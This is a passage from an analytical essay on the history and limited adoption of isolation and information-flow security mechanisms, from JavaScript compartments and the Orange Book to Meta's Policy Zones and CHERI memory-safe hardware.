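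Such packages are especially dangerous to a wallet, because one malicious update to an indirect dependency could steal users' keys. LavaMoat, MetaMask's set of tools against such attacks, runs each package under SES and gives it only the browser or system features that a policy file allows. A date-formatting package would normally get no network access, so a malicious update to it could not send a key anywhere on its own.

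LavaMoat's developers aim to protect existing applications without a rewrite. The tool can generate the policy file, whereas OpenJDK's complaints about the Security Manager included a lack of tools for working out permissions. Someone still has to check the generated policy, because if a package is already malicious, the policy may grant the permissions its code needs.

The security firm Least Authority audited MetaMask's plug-in system and found no way for a plug-in to escape its compartment. That audit assumed that SES itself worked, but the firm had examined SES separately in 2020 and found no breaches. By design, SES does not stop a plug-in from freezing the whole program with an endless loop. Compartments also start without a working clock, because code that can measure time precisely may be able to infer secrets held elsewhere in the same process. The project's site advises hosts that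 supply timers not to keep confidential information in that process.

Miller and others have tried to get more of this into JavaScript itself. TC39, the committee responsible, explores a proposal at Stage 1 and adds it to the standard at Stage 4. The Compartments proposal reached Stage 1 in April 2020. In *TC39 Compartments on Matrix*, Kowal (2022) saw a "sudden upwelling of political will" and hoped to reach Stage 2 soon, but Farias's *Compartments* entry in a catalogue of proposals still lists it at Stage 1, with no changes since December 2022.

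ShadowRealm, a related proposal for running code with a fresh set of global objects, advanced further but later returned to an earlier stage. It began in 2017 and in 2021 reached Stage 3, the signal for browsers to build it. Minor, in *ShadowRealm*, then presented Mozilla's argument for returning it to Stage 2, which was that it had too few tests and might affect a lot of browser code. By February 2025 it was at Stage 2.7, and Igalia's *Summary of the February 2025 TC39 plenary* (2025) reported that the main open question was whether browser makers wanted to build the parts that connect it to web pages. Marquis (2026), in *Banishing JavaScript to the ShadowRealm*, still described it as a proposal that November.

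Security is one reason browser makers are unenthusiastic about ShadowRealm. Chromium's developers warned in *Intent to Prototype* that it is "not a sufficient security boundary for many threat models", because the isolated code shares a process with everything else. Speculative execution attacks on processors, made public in 2018, can let code read memory elsewhere in its own process without breaking any rule of the language.

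### Old libraries or cheaper isolation

One explanation for this record is that programmers would have had to give up their libraries. This fits E, Joe-E and the early Caja well. It fits the Security Manager less well, because that came with a mainstream language and all its libraries and still went unused. However, few library authors had written their code with permissions in mind. Hardened JavaScript runs most existing code, yet it has found only a few specialised users.

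The other explanation is that browsers, processes and containers met most of the demand with less effort. It better explains how Caja and the Security Manager ended, because Google and Java's maintainers both recommended that kind of isolation as a replacement. But the two explanations overlap, since an iframe or a container takes little effort to adopt largely because the code inside it does not have to change. Capability languages still have some use where a developer needs to separate packages that call one another constantly within one program, which is awkward to do with processes.

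Some hosting platforms now combine process-style isolation with capabilities. On Cloudflare Workers, a service that runs customers' JavaScript, a developer lists the databases and other services a program may use, and the platform passes each one to the program as an object called a binding. The program never receives a database's password, and it cannot reach a database without a binding for it. Ordinary libraries work much as usual within these limits. By default, however, a program can contact any public web address, so some ambient authority remains.

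In September 2025 Cloudflare applied the same design to code written by AI agents. In its Code Mode, the model writes a short program that uses the agent's tools, and the program runs in a new sandbox with bindings to those tools and no other access to the internet. Because the model writes new code for each task, few existing libraries have to be ported. But an agent with a binding for sending mail can still write a program that mails a private document to the wrong person.

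## Why has information-flow control had so few users?

A capability can control whether a program may send mail, but not what the message contains. Information-flow control attaches labels to data and restricts where the data, and anything derived from it, may go. A program that has read a private document could then send mail only to people cleared to see that document. The US military began paying for operating systems with such labels in the 1960s, and language designers adopted the idea in the 1970s. Few organisations outside government and universities have used the resulting systems and languages, though Meta has recently become a large exception. Companies that worry about leaks more often buy data-loss-prevention software, which scans outgoing messages for patterns such as credit card numbers and can miss reworded or encrypted data.

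### Labels in a lattice

Dorothy Denning gave the field its standard mathematics in 1976. Every piece of data has a label, and A ⊑ B means that label B is at least as restrictive as label A, so data labeled A may flow to a place labeled B. The labels form a lattice, which means that any two have a least upper bound (the least restrictive label that is at least as restrictive as both) and a greatest lower bound. Data computed from two sources receives the least upper bound of their labels.

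A military label consists of a level and a set of compartments. Labels are ordered so that (L₁, C₁) ⊑ (L₂, C₂) exactly when L₁ ≤ L₂ and C₁ ⊆ C₂. A report that combines a (Secret, {Navy}) file with a (Confidential, {Nuclear}) file is therefore labeled (Secret, {Navy, Nuclear}). An officer cleared for (Top Secret, {Navy}) cannot read it, despite her higher level, because she lacks the Nuclear compartment.

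David Bell and Leonard LaPadula of MITRE, a research contractor, turned this ordering into two rules for operating systems in 1973. A program may read only data labeled at or below its own level, and write only to places labeled at or above it. The second rule is meant to stop hostile programs from leaking data. Suppose a general runs a game with spying code hidden in it. The game can read her Top Secret files because it runs with her clearance, but it cannot copy them into an unclassified file where someone else could read them.

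Kenneth Biba, also at MITRE, reversed the rules to protect integrity. In his version, a program may read only data at least as trustworthy as itself and write only to places no more trustworthy than itself, so a downloaded program cannot alter system files. Engineers call both sets of rules mandatory because users cannot override them, unlike ordinary file permissions, which are discretionary because a file's owner can share it with anyone.

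### Leaks that copy nothing

The obvious leak is an explicit flow, in which a program copies a secret into a public variable. The Portland State University lecture notes *Information-flow Security* give an example of a less obvious one. Let `h` be secret and `l` public, each either true or false:

```
l := False
if h { l := True }
```

No statement copies `h` into `l`, but the two are equal when the program ends. This is an implicit flow. A run-time monitor can easily miss it, because when `h` is false the assignment inside the braces never runs. The public variable `l` stays false, which reveals that `h` is false too. A compiler can catch the flow because it analyzes both branches. It can treat everything inside the `if` as dependent on `h` and reject any assignment there to a variable with a less restrictive label.

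In 1982, Joseph Goguen and José Meseguer defined the property that such checks are meant to enforce and called it noninterference. In its simplest form, noninterference requires that, for every public input *l* and every pair of secrets *h*₁ and *h*₂, running the program on (*h*₁, *l*) gives the same public output as running it on (*h*₂, *l*). The example violates this because changing `h` from false to true changes the final value of `l`.

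What counts as output depends on what the attacker can observe. The lecture notes' second example, `while h { }`, changes no variable, but it runs forever if `h` is true and stops if `h` is false. An information path like this, which nobody intended for communication, is called a covert channel. Two programs can also signal to each other by keeping the processor busy or locking a file. Designers of shared computers found that they could not close all these channels without slowing the machine badly, so they settled for limiting how fast the channels could carry data. US government guidance treated one bit per second as tolerable. At that rate, a 128-bit encryption key leaks in about two minutes, according to a comment in Neumann (2024), *Exploratory Investigation of Hardware-Software for Highly Assured Multilevel Security (MLS)*.

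Noninterference also rules out many useful programs. When a cash machine rejects a four-digit PIN, it reveals that the correct PIN is one of the other 9,999. Noninterference forbids this flow from secret to public, but a cash machine can't check PINs without it. Practical systems therefore allow declassification, a deliberate and authorised relaxation of a confidentiality label. But somebody has to decide which relaxations are safe, and that decision can't be checked using the labels.

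Too little declassification leads to label creep, the tendency of labels to grow more restrictive until they allow nothing useful. Suppose a calendar program reads one Secret appointment. The week's schedule becomes Secret, and so does the count of people expected for lunch, so the kitchen staff cannot read the count. Each step follows the rules, even though the count reveals almost nothing about the appointment. The designers can either withhold the count from the kitchen or add an exception.

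### The Orange Book

Anderson's 1972 study estimated that the lack of secure shared computers cost the Air Force $100 million a year. The government first paid contractors to build such computers. In the late 1970s it decided to evaluate commercial products instead, as Lipner recounts in *The Birth and Death of the Orange Book* (2015). A new center inside the National Security Agency (NSA) published the Trusted Computer System Evaluation Criteria, commonly called the Orange Book, in August 1983.

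It sorted products into classes. Class D was for products that offered minimal protection, and each higher class added requirements to those of the class below. The counts below are totals of the yearly evaluations Lipner lists, including repeat evaluations of new versions.

| Class | Main addition | Evaluations, 1984–1998 |
|---|---|---|
| C1 | Users control who can access their files | 1 |
| C2 | Audit records, and no leftover data in reused storage | 32 |
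| B1 | Labels and mandatory rules | 28 |
| B2 | A formal policy model and a structured design | 6 |
| B3 | A convincing argument that the design fits the model | 5 |
| A1 | Use of formal verification tools to show that it does | 4 |

The center's staff expected vendors to pass C2 quickly and then add labels. They nicknamed B1 "mandatory access control training wheels" because they thought the real work would begin at B2. By 1990, vendors had completed 12 evaluations at C2, but only three products had passed B1, and only two general-purpose operating systems, Honeywell's Multics and SCOMP, had reached B2 or higher.

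In 1987 a government committee required agencies handling national security information to use C2 systems, and the center adopted the slogan "C2 by '92". Class C2 has no labels, so a program meant to spread information-flow control ended up promoting ordinary file permissions and audit logs. It promoted those features fairly well. Evaluations peaked at 17 in 1994, and *Musings on a Book of Orange*, a practitioner's retrospective, counts the slogan among the reasons Windows NT had stronger security than earlier versions of Windows. Lipner leaves open whether vendors would have added the same features anyway.

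Evaluation was slow and unpredictable even at the lower classes. IBM expected RACF to pass at C2, but it received C1. Discussion at the time centered on RACF's failure to ensure that new files contained no data from deleted ones, a control that IBM's engineers thought would slow the system too much. Evaluators asked vendors for design documents that the Orange Book did not require at C2 or B1, and vendors hired people to write them for the evaluators. One evaluator defined "security relevant" as "anything which the evaluation community feels may be relevant to system security". Another vendor had an access control mechanism resembling capabilities, and the evaluators made the vendor build a tool to report who could access what, which administrators had also found difficult to determine in KeyKOS.

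These delays made labeled systems expensive, and people also found them hard to use. The Naval Research Laboratory's Military Message Experiment applied the Bell-LaPadula rules to electronic mail, and Lipner reports that the result was almost unusable. Suppose an officer reads a Secret message and wants to send an unclassified reply saying "Thursday is fine". She is working at the Secret level, so her reply would write to a lower level, and the system has to block it until she declassifies the text through a separate procedure.

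The usual remedy was a trusted process, a program exempt from the rules. Every such program becomes part of the trusted computing base. Researchers complained that the systems were unusable without these exceptions and that the exceptions undermined the mathematical model. Tom Van Vleck, a Multics developer, recalls in Neumann's report that even the staff running the NSA's own Multics system made local changes to the rules that were "probably 'illegal'".

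Labels seem to have worked better where information needed to move in only one direction. At the Air Force Data Services Center, programmers with Secret clearances wrote models that analysts then applied to Top Secret data, and the results could stay at the Top Secret level. Lipner cites informal reports that mandatory controls were useful at the center, though he adds that common tasks there would also have required writing information to a lower level.

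By the late 1990s independent researchers were publishing holes in commercial software, and Lipner writes that evaluated products "fared no better under attack than any others". This is strong evidence against the evaluations but much weaker evidence against labels, because nearly half the evaluations were at classes without labels and very few reached the classes that demanded a rigorous design. In 2014 the US body in charge concluded that broad evaluations of operating systems were not worth their cost.

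### Digital's VAX security kernel

Digital Equipment Corporation came closest to offering a mainstream computer at the top class. Its VAX/SVS project was a virtual machine monitor, software that runs several operating systems at once on one machine. Each virtual machine could have its own label, so customers could keep their existing operating systems and programs. *Lessons from VAX/SVS for High-Assurance VM Systems* (Lipner, Jaeger and Zurko, 2012) draws lessons from the project about access control, layering and verification.

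Digital conceived the project in 1981 and had a prototype running by 1984. The finished kernel had about 50,000 lines of code, and customers began testing it in late 1989. The tests went well, and the developers were confident of an A1 rating, although they never completed the formal specification that A1 required.

Lipner, the manager responsible at Digital, cancelled the project in 1990 because he did not expect enough people to buy the system. The hardware it ran on was near the end of its life, and the team had left out Ethernet support to save time. Export rules would have made sales difficult even to close NATO allies. Above all, the system was designed for time-sharing, and customers were moving to workstations. Digital could have paid to fix some of these problems, but did not expect to earn the money back. Some of Lipner's colleagues thought there were enough buyers.

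Other vendors' results support his decision. Honeywell sold fewer than 30 of the original SCOMP systems and never broke even. Its marketing staff estimated that a later version would gain five percent at best from an A1 rating instead of B3. IBM built a B2 version of the Xenix operating system and gave it away to a security consultancy. Buyers who had said they needed high security often waived the requirement when they saw what else was for sale. A secure system took years to develop and evaluate, so by the time it was ready it cost more and did less than its competitors. Low sales then raised the price further.

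Cheap hardware also removed much of the original need for labeled systems. In a statement for Neumann's report, Lipner says they were meant to spare the government from giving each user several computers. As personal computers got cheaper, several computers became more practical than one labeled machine. An official can have a Secret machine and an unclassified one with no connection between them, which is also a guarantee by construction, though a coarse one. Labeled operating systems therefore lost, much as Caja did, to a simpler kind of isolation that required less of the software inside it.

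### What the insiders concluded

Steven Bellovin, a network security researcher, is harsher than Lipner. In a 1997 slide titled *What to Do?*, he complained that the Orange Book "doesn't protect the right things". In his statement for Neumann, he calls such labeled systems a dead end, giving an online shop as an example. Customers arrive over the internet without any clearance, so the web server has to run as unclassified, but it needs their credit card numbers. To protect customers from each other, every customer would need a separate compartment, and the billing system would need access to all of them. Bellovin tried to build a labeled system for sensitive internal data at AT&T in about 1999. He gave up because it needed trusted programs in many places to move data between levels, and he had no assurance that their many authors would write them correctly.

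Bellovin also questions whether the Orange Book addressed the right attacks. After the Internet Worm of 1988 spread through thousands of machines, he reread the book and concluded that nothing in it would have stopped the worm. The book assumed a trusted kernel and untrusted applications, but the most troublesome holes of recent years have been in applications. An attacker who takes over a hospital's records program can read the records without touching the kernel. Bellovin compares security to building walls, which engineers do well, but every useful system has doors in its walls, and somebody has to decide what may pass through them.

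Three later systems, Asbestos, HiStar and Flume, published between 2005 and 2007, dealt with part of the online shop problem by letting ordinary programs create their own labels. A web server could then give each user's data a separate label without asking an administrator. These systems still needed trusted code to release data beyond what its label allowed, and they remained research prototypes.

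Lipner largely agrees with Bellovin. He writes that there was no commercial demand because companies' policies do not resemble military classification, and that the government did not buy the systems industry tried to build for it. Neumann, who worked on several of the early systems and calls himself a "conservative optimist", is more hopeful about tightly constrained uses on new hardware.

One descendant of information-flow control did reach majority use. Windows has applied a variation on Biba's integrity rules since Vista in 2007. A program running at low integrity, such as the part of a browser that handles web pages, cannot modify files or settings at a higher level. Microsoft supplies the few levels and most of the labels, and by default Windows restricts writing but lets a trusted program read untrusted files. Even so, Lipner says, users needed a way to change a setting or install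 a program, and Microsoft spent several releases adjusting how strictly it enforced the rules.

### Jif and the cost of annotations

An operating system usually labels whole files and processes, which is one reason for label creep. If a program reads one secret and a thousand public facts, everything it writes is labeled secret. A programming language can label individual variables. Zdancewic's 2003 lecture slides list this precision as a main benefit of the language approach, along with control over data throughout a program.

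Jif, which Andrew Myers introduced in 1999 under the name JFlow, adds labels to Java. A programmer who writes `int{Alice:Bob} salary` declares a number that Alice owns and lets Bob read. The compiler follows the number through the program, including through implicit flows, and rejects any code that could reveal it to Carol. Only code that runs with Alice's authority can declassify it. Most checks happen before the program runs, so they add little run-time overhead.

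Information-flow control makes more work for programmers when they write code. In Jif, an extension of Java, they have to label variables and the inputs and results of functions, and any library they call needs a labeled description. They also have to handle errors that Java lets them ignore, because a program that crashes only when a secret has a certain value reveals something about the secret. Jif leaves out Java's threads, since the order in which parallel tasks finish can leak information.

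*SIF* (Chong, Vikram and Myers, 2007) extended the approach to web applications. Policies could come from the programmer's annotations or from requirements that users set while the program ran, and the same analysis could help against attacks such as SQL injection, in which a database runs an attacker's input as a command. Most programmers who used Jif and its successors were researchers. A policy that protects a hospital's patients may be worth months of annotation, but a company would also have to replace or describe every library it uses, and its customers cannot see the added security.

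Zdancewic described three obstacles in a 2004 paper, *Challenges for Information-flow Security*. Labeled programs have to work with existing operating systems, files and networks, which don't support the labels. Noninterference is too strict, so programs need controlled exceptions to it. Policies also become hard to manage as a program grows. The military systems had already faced all three problems. Languages made labels more precise, but programmers had to get many more of them right.

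Extensive research has not brought information-flow control many users. In a primer on the method, Geoffrey Smith noted that one survey cited about 150 papers, then discussed the challenges that had so far kept the method from much practical use. By the late 2010s, designers had too many versions to choose from. In *Prudent Design Principles for Information Flow Control* (2018), Bastys, Piessens and Sabelfeld describe "a bewildering breed of concepts, policies, conditions, and enforcement mechanisms". They wrote the paper to help designers decide what security should mean for a new application before choosing how to enforce it.

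### Ruby gives up on taint

Taint checking is a much simpler form of information-flow control than Jif. It uses two integrity labels, tainted and clean. The language marks data from outside the program as tainted, keeps the mark when the program copies or combines the data, and blocks tainted data from dangerous operations until the programmer has checked it. It generally does not track implicit flows. Perl introduced taint checking, and Ruby, a language popular for websites, copied it. Programmers did not have to write any labels, so the work of annotation was not a reason to avoid it.

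In 2019 Yui Naruse's *Remove $SAFE, taint and trust* proposed that Ruby drop the feature. He wrote that some people had used it in the early days of the web but nobody did any more. He also ran a small test with Rack, the library through which most Ruby web applications receive requests. Text that a visitor types into a web address arrived without a taint mark, even though an attacker controls that text.

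An earlier request, *$SAFE should be removed*, had explained why in a discussion that ran into 2012. Taint protects a program only if all code, including extensions written in C, handles the marks properly. If one library omits a mark, hostile data looks clean and nothing visibly breaks. Ruby's taint was meant as a guarantee, but in practice it was one of the exclusion-based mechanisms that Saltzer and Schroeder had warned about. A stricter version could have treated all data as tainted until somebody marked it clean, but that would have stopped many working programs.

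Whenever Ruby joined two pieces of text, it had to check whether either was tainted, even for people who never used the feature. Naruse pointed to several past vulnerabilities in the mechanism and to the work of maintaining it. None of the core developers who replied defended it, and one programmer admitted that he used taint marks to remember which objects he had changed. Removing the feature still meant changing about 25 code repositories. Ruby 2.7 made the functions do nothing in 2019. Ruby's source code then carried the notice that "taintedness turned out to be a wrong idea" until Ruby 3.2 deleted the functions in 2022.

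### Policy Zones at Meta

Meta has since deployed information-flow control on a far larger scale than any of the earlier projects. According to Waye (2025), its Policy Zones system runs across the company's infrastructure and enforces purpose limitation, the principle that a company may use personal data only for the purposes it has stated. For instance, Meta might be allowed to use data about when people send messages to catch spam, but not to choose advertisements.

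Meta had tried simpler methods first. Programmers wrote checks into the code wherever it used restricted data, and access control lists protected each dataset. Both needed frequent audits, because anyone who could read a dataset could copy it into a new one with different permissions. The lists also worked only if Meta kept data for different purposes in physically separate places, but the same code often processed all of it. According to Meta (2024), these methods did not scale once the requirements crossed dozens of systems. Tracing where data had gone could reveal a wrongful transfer only after it had happened.

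Meta (2025) explains how Policy Zones works in the company's data warehouse, using an engineer who wants a daily count of the messages each user sends:

1. The source table has the label MESSAGING_DATA, which a central configuration links to a list of allowed purposes.
2. The engineer writes a query in SQL, the standard database language. A parser works out which tables the query reads and which it writes.
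3. A policy service checks that the purpose is allowed and that the output table has the same label. If it doesn't, the system adds the label when the intention is clear, or stops and offers the engineer ways to fix the problem.
4. If the flow passes, the service issues a cryptographically signed token, and the warehouse checks the token before it grants access to the data.

The third step follows Denning's rule that the restrictions on derived data must be at least as strict as those on its source. Because an SQL query specifies what it reads and writes, the system can often check a flow without analysing a program line by line. Implicit flows also matter less when a label covers a whole table, because the output needs the label whether the query copies the messaging data or only uses it to decide which rows to include.

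In Meta's websites and other services, the system works on requests instead of queries. A request that loads labeled data enters a zone, and the system blocks it from writing to any log or database outside that zone.

The warehouse version controls access to millions of datasets and analyses tens of millions of data flows a day. It checks trillions of times an hour whether users have consented to a particular use. These are Meta's own figures, and nobody has published anything close to them for a comparable system.

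The system also took a lot of labor. A single complex requirement may involve hundreds or thousands of engineers, because the owners of each piece of code and data have to take part. Integrating the system with Meta's other software took years. Early versions slowed busy systems too much, and engineers found the labels hard to understand. Meta says it made the checks ten times more efficient and, after concentrating on correctness first, built tools that cut the engineering work by orders of magnitude.

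Policy Zones starts in a logging mode that records violations without blocking them, so engineers can see what a new label would break before it is enforced. In the warehouse, it can also suspend enforcement for individual flows until someone fixes them. The Orange Book's customers could not phase in enforcement this way, because a labeled operating system blocked forbidden flows from its first day.

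Meta also ran into label creep. It uses reclassification, a form of declassification that lets an engineer stop a label from spreading if the output no longer contains anything sensitive. Each label has its own rules for reclassification, which may require a review by human experts or a mathematical method of hiding individuals in the results. Meta had first tried a more expressive policy language that captured most special cases and needed no reclassification, but engineers could not work out why the system had blocked them. The company switched to plain, independent labels and used reclassification for the special cases. This makes the everyday rules easy to follow, but the system can no longer guarantee that some of the hardest decisions are correct.

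The guarantee has other limits. Meta relies heavily on a machine-learning classifier, and also on manual inspection, to find the data that needs a label, so a heuristic helps decide what the guarantee covers. Some programs in the warehouse are not written in SQL, and where the system cannot track their data, Meta still keeps that data separate. Systems without Policy Zones use the old checks.

A privacy obligation could justify all this work because violations could lead to large fines. The European Union's data protection law, which took effect in 2018, makes purpose limitation a legal duty and allows fines of up to 4% of a company's worldwide turnover. Meta's posts mention privacy requirements and commitments but not this law, so it is unclear how much the law influenced the decision. Purpose limitation suits information-flow control unusually well, because it restricts what may happen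 to data after someone has legitimately read it, and access control alone cannot enforce that.

Meta was also in a better position than the Orange Book's vendors. It owned the data and the software and employed the engineers, so it could order the labeling done without having to persuade customers to buy anything. Keeping data on separate computers had become cheaper than labels for the military but more expensive for Meta. Policy Zones mostly has to stop well-meaning engineers from using data for the wrong purpose, while the military systems had to withstand hostile programs that might leak a key one bit at a time.

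## Why is memory-safe hardware still scarce?

Capsicum, Jif and Policy Zones all required people to label data or reorganise programs. A processor could in principle spare them most of that work, because it already carries out every program's memory accesses. In 1981 Intel sold a processor that enforced capabilities, and a much better design called CHERI has been in development since 2010. But by late 2026 almost nobody could buy a computer with a CHERI processor, while Apple's newest phones and laptops had a weaker protection that relied partly on chance.

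### Pointers that carry their own limits

A pointer gives the location of something in memory. On an ordinary processor it is only a number, and a program can use any number as an address. The program therefore has a kind of ambient authority over all its own memory, and a bug that changes a pointer changes what the program reads or overwrites.

CHERI, a project of Cambridge University and the research institute SRI International, replaces ordinary numeric pointers with capabilities. Its draft specification for RISC-V, an instruction set that any chip designer may use, widens each pointer on a 64-bit machine to 128 bits (RISC-V International, 2024). Half of those bits hold the address, and the rest hold permissions, such as the right to read or write, and two bounds, called base and top. The program may use the pointer to access address *A* only if base ≤ *A* < top.

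One more bit, the tag, records whether the 128 bits are a valid capability. The hardware keeps a tag for every 16-byte block of memory that could hold a pointer. No address refers to the tags, so a program cannot set them itself. If an ordinary instruction writes even one byte of a block, the hardware clears that block's tag. Using a pointer whose tag has been cleared causes a fault, and the processor stops the program or passes control to an error handler.

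When the machine starts, software receives a few root capabilities that typically cover all of memory. It derives every other capability from these, and each step can keep or reduce the bounds and permissions but never extend them. So no sequence of instructions, however hostile, can produce a capability that grants more access than the ones it started with. KeyKOS enforced the same rule in its kernel, but CHERI applies it to every pointer in a program.

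The designers had trouble fitting the bounds into pointers. An early version used 256-bit pointers, which made the hardware very expensive. The current format compresses the bounds, roughly as a computer stores decimal fractions, so they are exact for small objects but rounded for large ones. The software that allocates memory therefore has to leave padding around large objects.

### One overflow, step by step

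Suppose the journalist's PDF reader opens a file that declares an image to be 64 bytes long when it is actually 80. The reader sets aside 64 bytes starting at address 4096. The next object in memory, at address 4160, holds a pointer to the code that the reader will run afterwards. On an ordinary processor, the reader copies all 80 bytes, the last 16 overwrite that pointer, and the reader runs whatever code the attacker chose.

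On a CHERI processor, the same program behaves differently:

1. The memory allocator, which hands out memory, returns a capability with base 4096 and top 4160.
2. The reader copies the first 64 bytes to addresses 4096 to 4159, and each write passes the check.
3. The 65th byte would go to address 4160, which is not below the top. The processor raises a fault before it writes the byte.
4. The reader crashes, or an error handler discards the image.

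The tag helps when the bounds are too wide. If the image buffer and the pointer are parts of one larger object, the copying code may hold a capability to the whole object, so the overflow stays within bounds. The overflow overwrites the pointer but also clears its tag, so the program faults when it tries to use the pointer. If the neighboring field were an ordinary number, such as a flag marking whether the user is an administrator, the overflow would change it without causing a fault.

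CHERI needs an extra step to protect freed memory, because old pointers to it still have valid tags. The system can search for those pointers and clear their tags before it reuses the memory. *CHERI is being standardised* (Moore, 2026) lists this among the parts of the design that researchers now understand well.

### Sixteen colors

Arm, whose processor designs are in nearly all phones, announced a less demanding scheme called the Memory Tagging Extension (MTE) in 2018. It gives each 16-byte block of memory one of 16 values, which engineers often call colors, and stores a color in unused bits at the top of each pointer. If the pointer's color differs from the memory's, the processor can raise a fault.

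In the PDF example, the image buffer might have color 9 and the next object color 3, so the 65th byte causes a fault here too. An allocator that always gives neighbors different colors catches every overflow from one object into the next. But some bugs let an attacker choose a distant address, and the color there matches by chance about one time in 16. As with address randomization, repeated guesses help the attacker, and ten independent attempts have about a 48% chance of at least one match.

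MTE also has no equivalent of CHERI's tag bit, so an attacker who knows the right color can write a working pointer as ordinary data. In 2024, researchers from Seoul National University and Samsung published TikTag, an attack that uses the processor's speculative execution to discover colors. 8kSec's *Memory Integrity Enforcement (MIE) on iOS Deep Dive* describes how Apple's scheme responds to this.

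Apple introduced Memory Integrity Enforcement with the iPhone 17 in September 2025. It combines a stricter version of MTE, in which the processor faults immediately if a pointer's tag doesn't match the memory's tag, with allocators that keep different types of data apart and measures to keep the tags secret. It is always on for the kernel and more than 70 system processes. Apple includes it in devices with A19 and M5 processors or later.

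| Attack | CHERI | Arm's MTE | Apple's scheme |
|---|---|---|---|
| Overflow into the next object | Always stopped | Always stopped if neighbors have different colors | Always stopped, since neighbors have different colors |
| Out-of-bounds access to a distant object | Always stopped | Probably stopped | Probably stopped, and data types are kept apart |
| Fake pointer written as data | Always stopped | Probably stopped unless the color leaks | Probably stopped, and colors are harder to learn |
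| Use of memory after release and reuse | Always stopped if the system clears old pointers first | Probably stopped | Probably stopped, and data types are kept apart |

Even with these gaps, memory tagging can make attacks much harder. The security firm Calif reports that Apple spent five years on its scheme and found that it disrupts every public exploit chain against modern iOS.

### Two failures at Intel

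Intel's iAPX 432, released in 1981, checked capabilities in hardware for every object a program used. Intel designed it for programs written in Ada, a language the US military had commissioned, rather than for existing software. It was also several times slower than ordinary processors when researchers at Berkeley ran small programs on it in 1982, and The New York Times reported that it was five to ten times slower than its competitor, the Motorola 68000.

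For years afterwards, engineers cited the 432 as evidence that capability hardware was inherently slow. In 1988, Robert Colwell, Edward Gehringer and Douglas Jensen published a more careful study, in which they traced much of the delay to other causes, including a lack of fast on-chip storage for data and a poor compiler. The compiler used the slowest, fully protected kind of procedure call even where a simple one would have been safe. By then, Intel had abandoned the 432 and was selling very large numbers of ordinary processors that ran existing PC software.

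Intel tried again in 2015 with Memory Protection Extensions (MPX), which added bounds checks to its mainstream processors. Pointers stayed the same size, so MPX kept most bounds in separate tables, and the compiler had to insert instructions to look them up and check them. *Intel MPX Explained* (Oleksenko et al., 2018) found that programs took about 50% longer on average with the better of two compilers, and were about four times slower in the worst cases. Between 3% and 10% of the test programs did not compile or run correctly. MPX also did not prevent programs from using memory after releasing it, and two parallel tasks could leave a pointer matched with the wrong bounds.

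MPX let old libraries keep working, but this weakened its protection. If a library compiled without MPX changed a pointer, the pointer no longer matched its entry in the table, and the processor then let it access all of memory. The protection disappeared silently, as Ruby's taint marks did. In CHERI, by contrast, a pointer that ordinary code has overwritten stops working. The GCC compiler's developers removed MPX support in 2019, Linux followed in 2020, and Intel left MPX out of later processors.

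CHERI avoids several of these problems. The bounds travel with the pointer, the processor checks them as part of the memory access, and most C programs need only small changes. Slow or incompatible design is therefore a good explanation for Intel's two failures but a weaker one for CHERI's slow adoption.

### Morello and the British government

DARPA, the US military's research agency, paid for CHERI's early development. In 2019 the British government started a program called Digital Security by Design, which funded Arm to build Morello. Morello is an experimental computer board with four CHERI processor cores based on an existing commercial design. Arm made only a limited number of boards, at a cost of around $10,000 each.

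The government then asked who might buy the technology. DSIT's *CHERI adoption and diffusion research* (2024), a study for the UK's science and technology department, combined market statistics with interviews, a survey and a database of 394 firms that might use CHERI. The survey had only 14 respondents, 11 of whom had already heard of CHERI. In an earlier survey, in 2022, only about a quarter had. The study warns that both surveys may overstate awareness because people already involved with CHERI helped to promote them. The interviews and the sector analysis are more useful than these survey figures.

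According to the study, market forces had failed to fix insecure hardware for three reasons. Manufacturers do not make hardware that has no software, developers do not write software for hardware that does not exist, and consumers do not ask for safer chips because they are largely unaware of the risk. The study concludes that many of the significant barriers are economic rather than technical.

According to the study, phones are unlikely to adopt CHERI soon. Phone chips are expensive to redesign, and CHERI would take up chip space that could go to features customers want more. Google or Apple might also need thousands or even millions of engineering hours to recompile and adapt their software. The study predicted that small embedded devices, such as sensors and industrial controllers, would adopt CHERI first because their processors are simpler and many have little existing software to adapt.

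The program had more success with small firms than with the large companies that could have put CHERI into millions of devices. One part of it gave out nearly 40 Morello boards, mostly to small and medium-sized companies, and the study found its incentives too small to attract large ones. The projects showed that the technology works but provided less evidence that it is commercially worthwhile.

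### Fifteen teams port their software

Dstl, the British defense ministry's research laboratory, gave Morello boards and funding to 15 teams from companies and universities for up to 12 months. Each team chose its own software, with choices including drone controls, a smart camera and a Python interpreter. In *Biting the CHERI bullet*, Faily (2025) marked and grouped recurring themes in the teams' final reports. Faily did this alone, and the software differed too much for a common numerical measure, so the study is better evidence of what went wrong than of how often the same problems would occur elsewhere.

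Porting code to CHERI could take very few changes. One team ported a 216,650-line library by adding ten lines to set up the tools and changing 39 lines to build the library and its examples. This supports the claim that CHERI works with old code, but Faily points out that finding the lines to change sometimes took a long time. For instance, a common build tool uses pointer size to determine whether a machine is 32-bit or 64-bit, and CHERI's 128-bit pointers broke this check.

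Faily grouped the obstacles into six kinds: dependencies on other software, scarce knowledge, missing tools, slower programs, unstable hardware and software, and cleaning up old code. Several teams found that packages they relied on had not been ported. Instructions were out of date or contradicted one another, and one team could debug code in isolated compartments only by adding print statements. One popular communication framework lost up to 35% of its throughput, although the teams could not tell whether CHERI itself, the experimental board or mistakes in porting caused such losses.

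Faily also questioned how much CHERI protects by default, judging that it addressed only two of the ten most dangerous kinds of software weakness on a current industry list. CHERI could protect against use of released memory, but Faily expected this to break some existing programs. Default compiler settings gave up some protection for compatibility. CHERI also turns a memory error into a fault, so a drone's control software might stop in mid-air instead of being hijacked, and developers would have to plan for that.

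The teams did report benefits beyond security. CHERI found bugs that other tools had missed, and one team thought it worth testing software on Morello even if customers would run it on ordinary chips. Such testing would improve the software but create little demand for CHERI processors, since a company needs only a few machines for it.

### What someone can buy in 2026

The closest thing to an ordinary CHERI product is ICENI, a family of microcontrollers from the British company SCI Semiconductor. A microcontroller is a small, self-contained computer chip for equipment such as pumps or door locks. ICENI uses CHERIoT, a small version of CHERI that Microsoft developed for connected devices.

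The chip has taken longer than planned. lowRISC, a non-profit that helped develop the underlying design, had announced a commercial chip for the second half of 2025. According to CHERIoT (2025), the project that maintains the design, the first chips were still on their way back from the factory that November, and SCI intended to begin mass production in 2026. CHERIoT's *ICENI on a development board* (2026), written by an SCI co-founder, showed a working chip running at up to 250 MHz in March.

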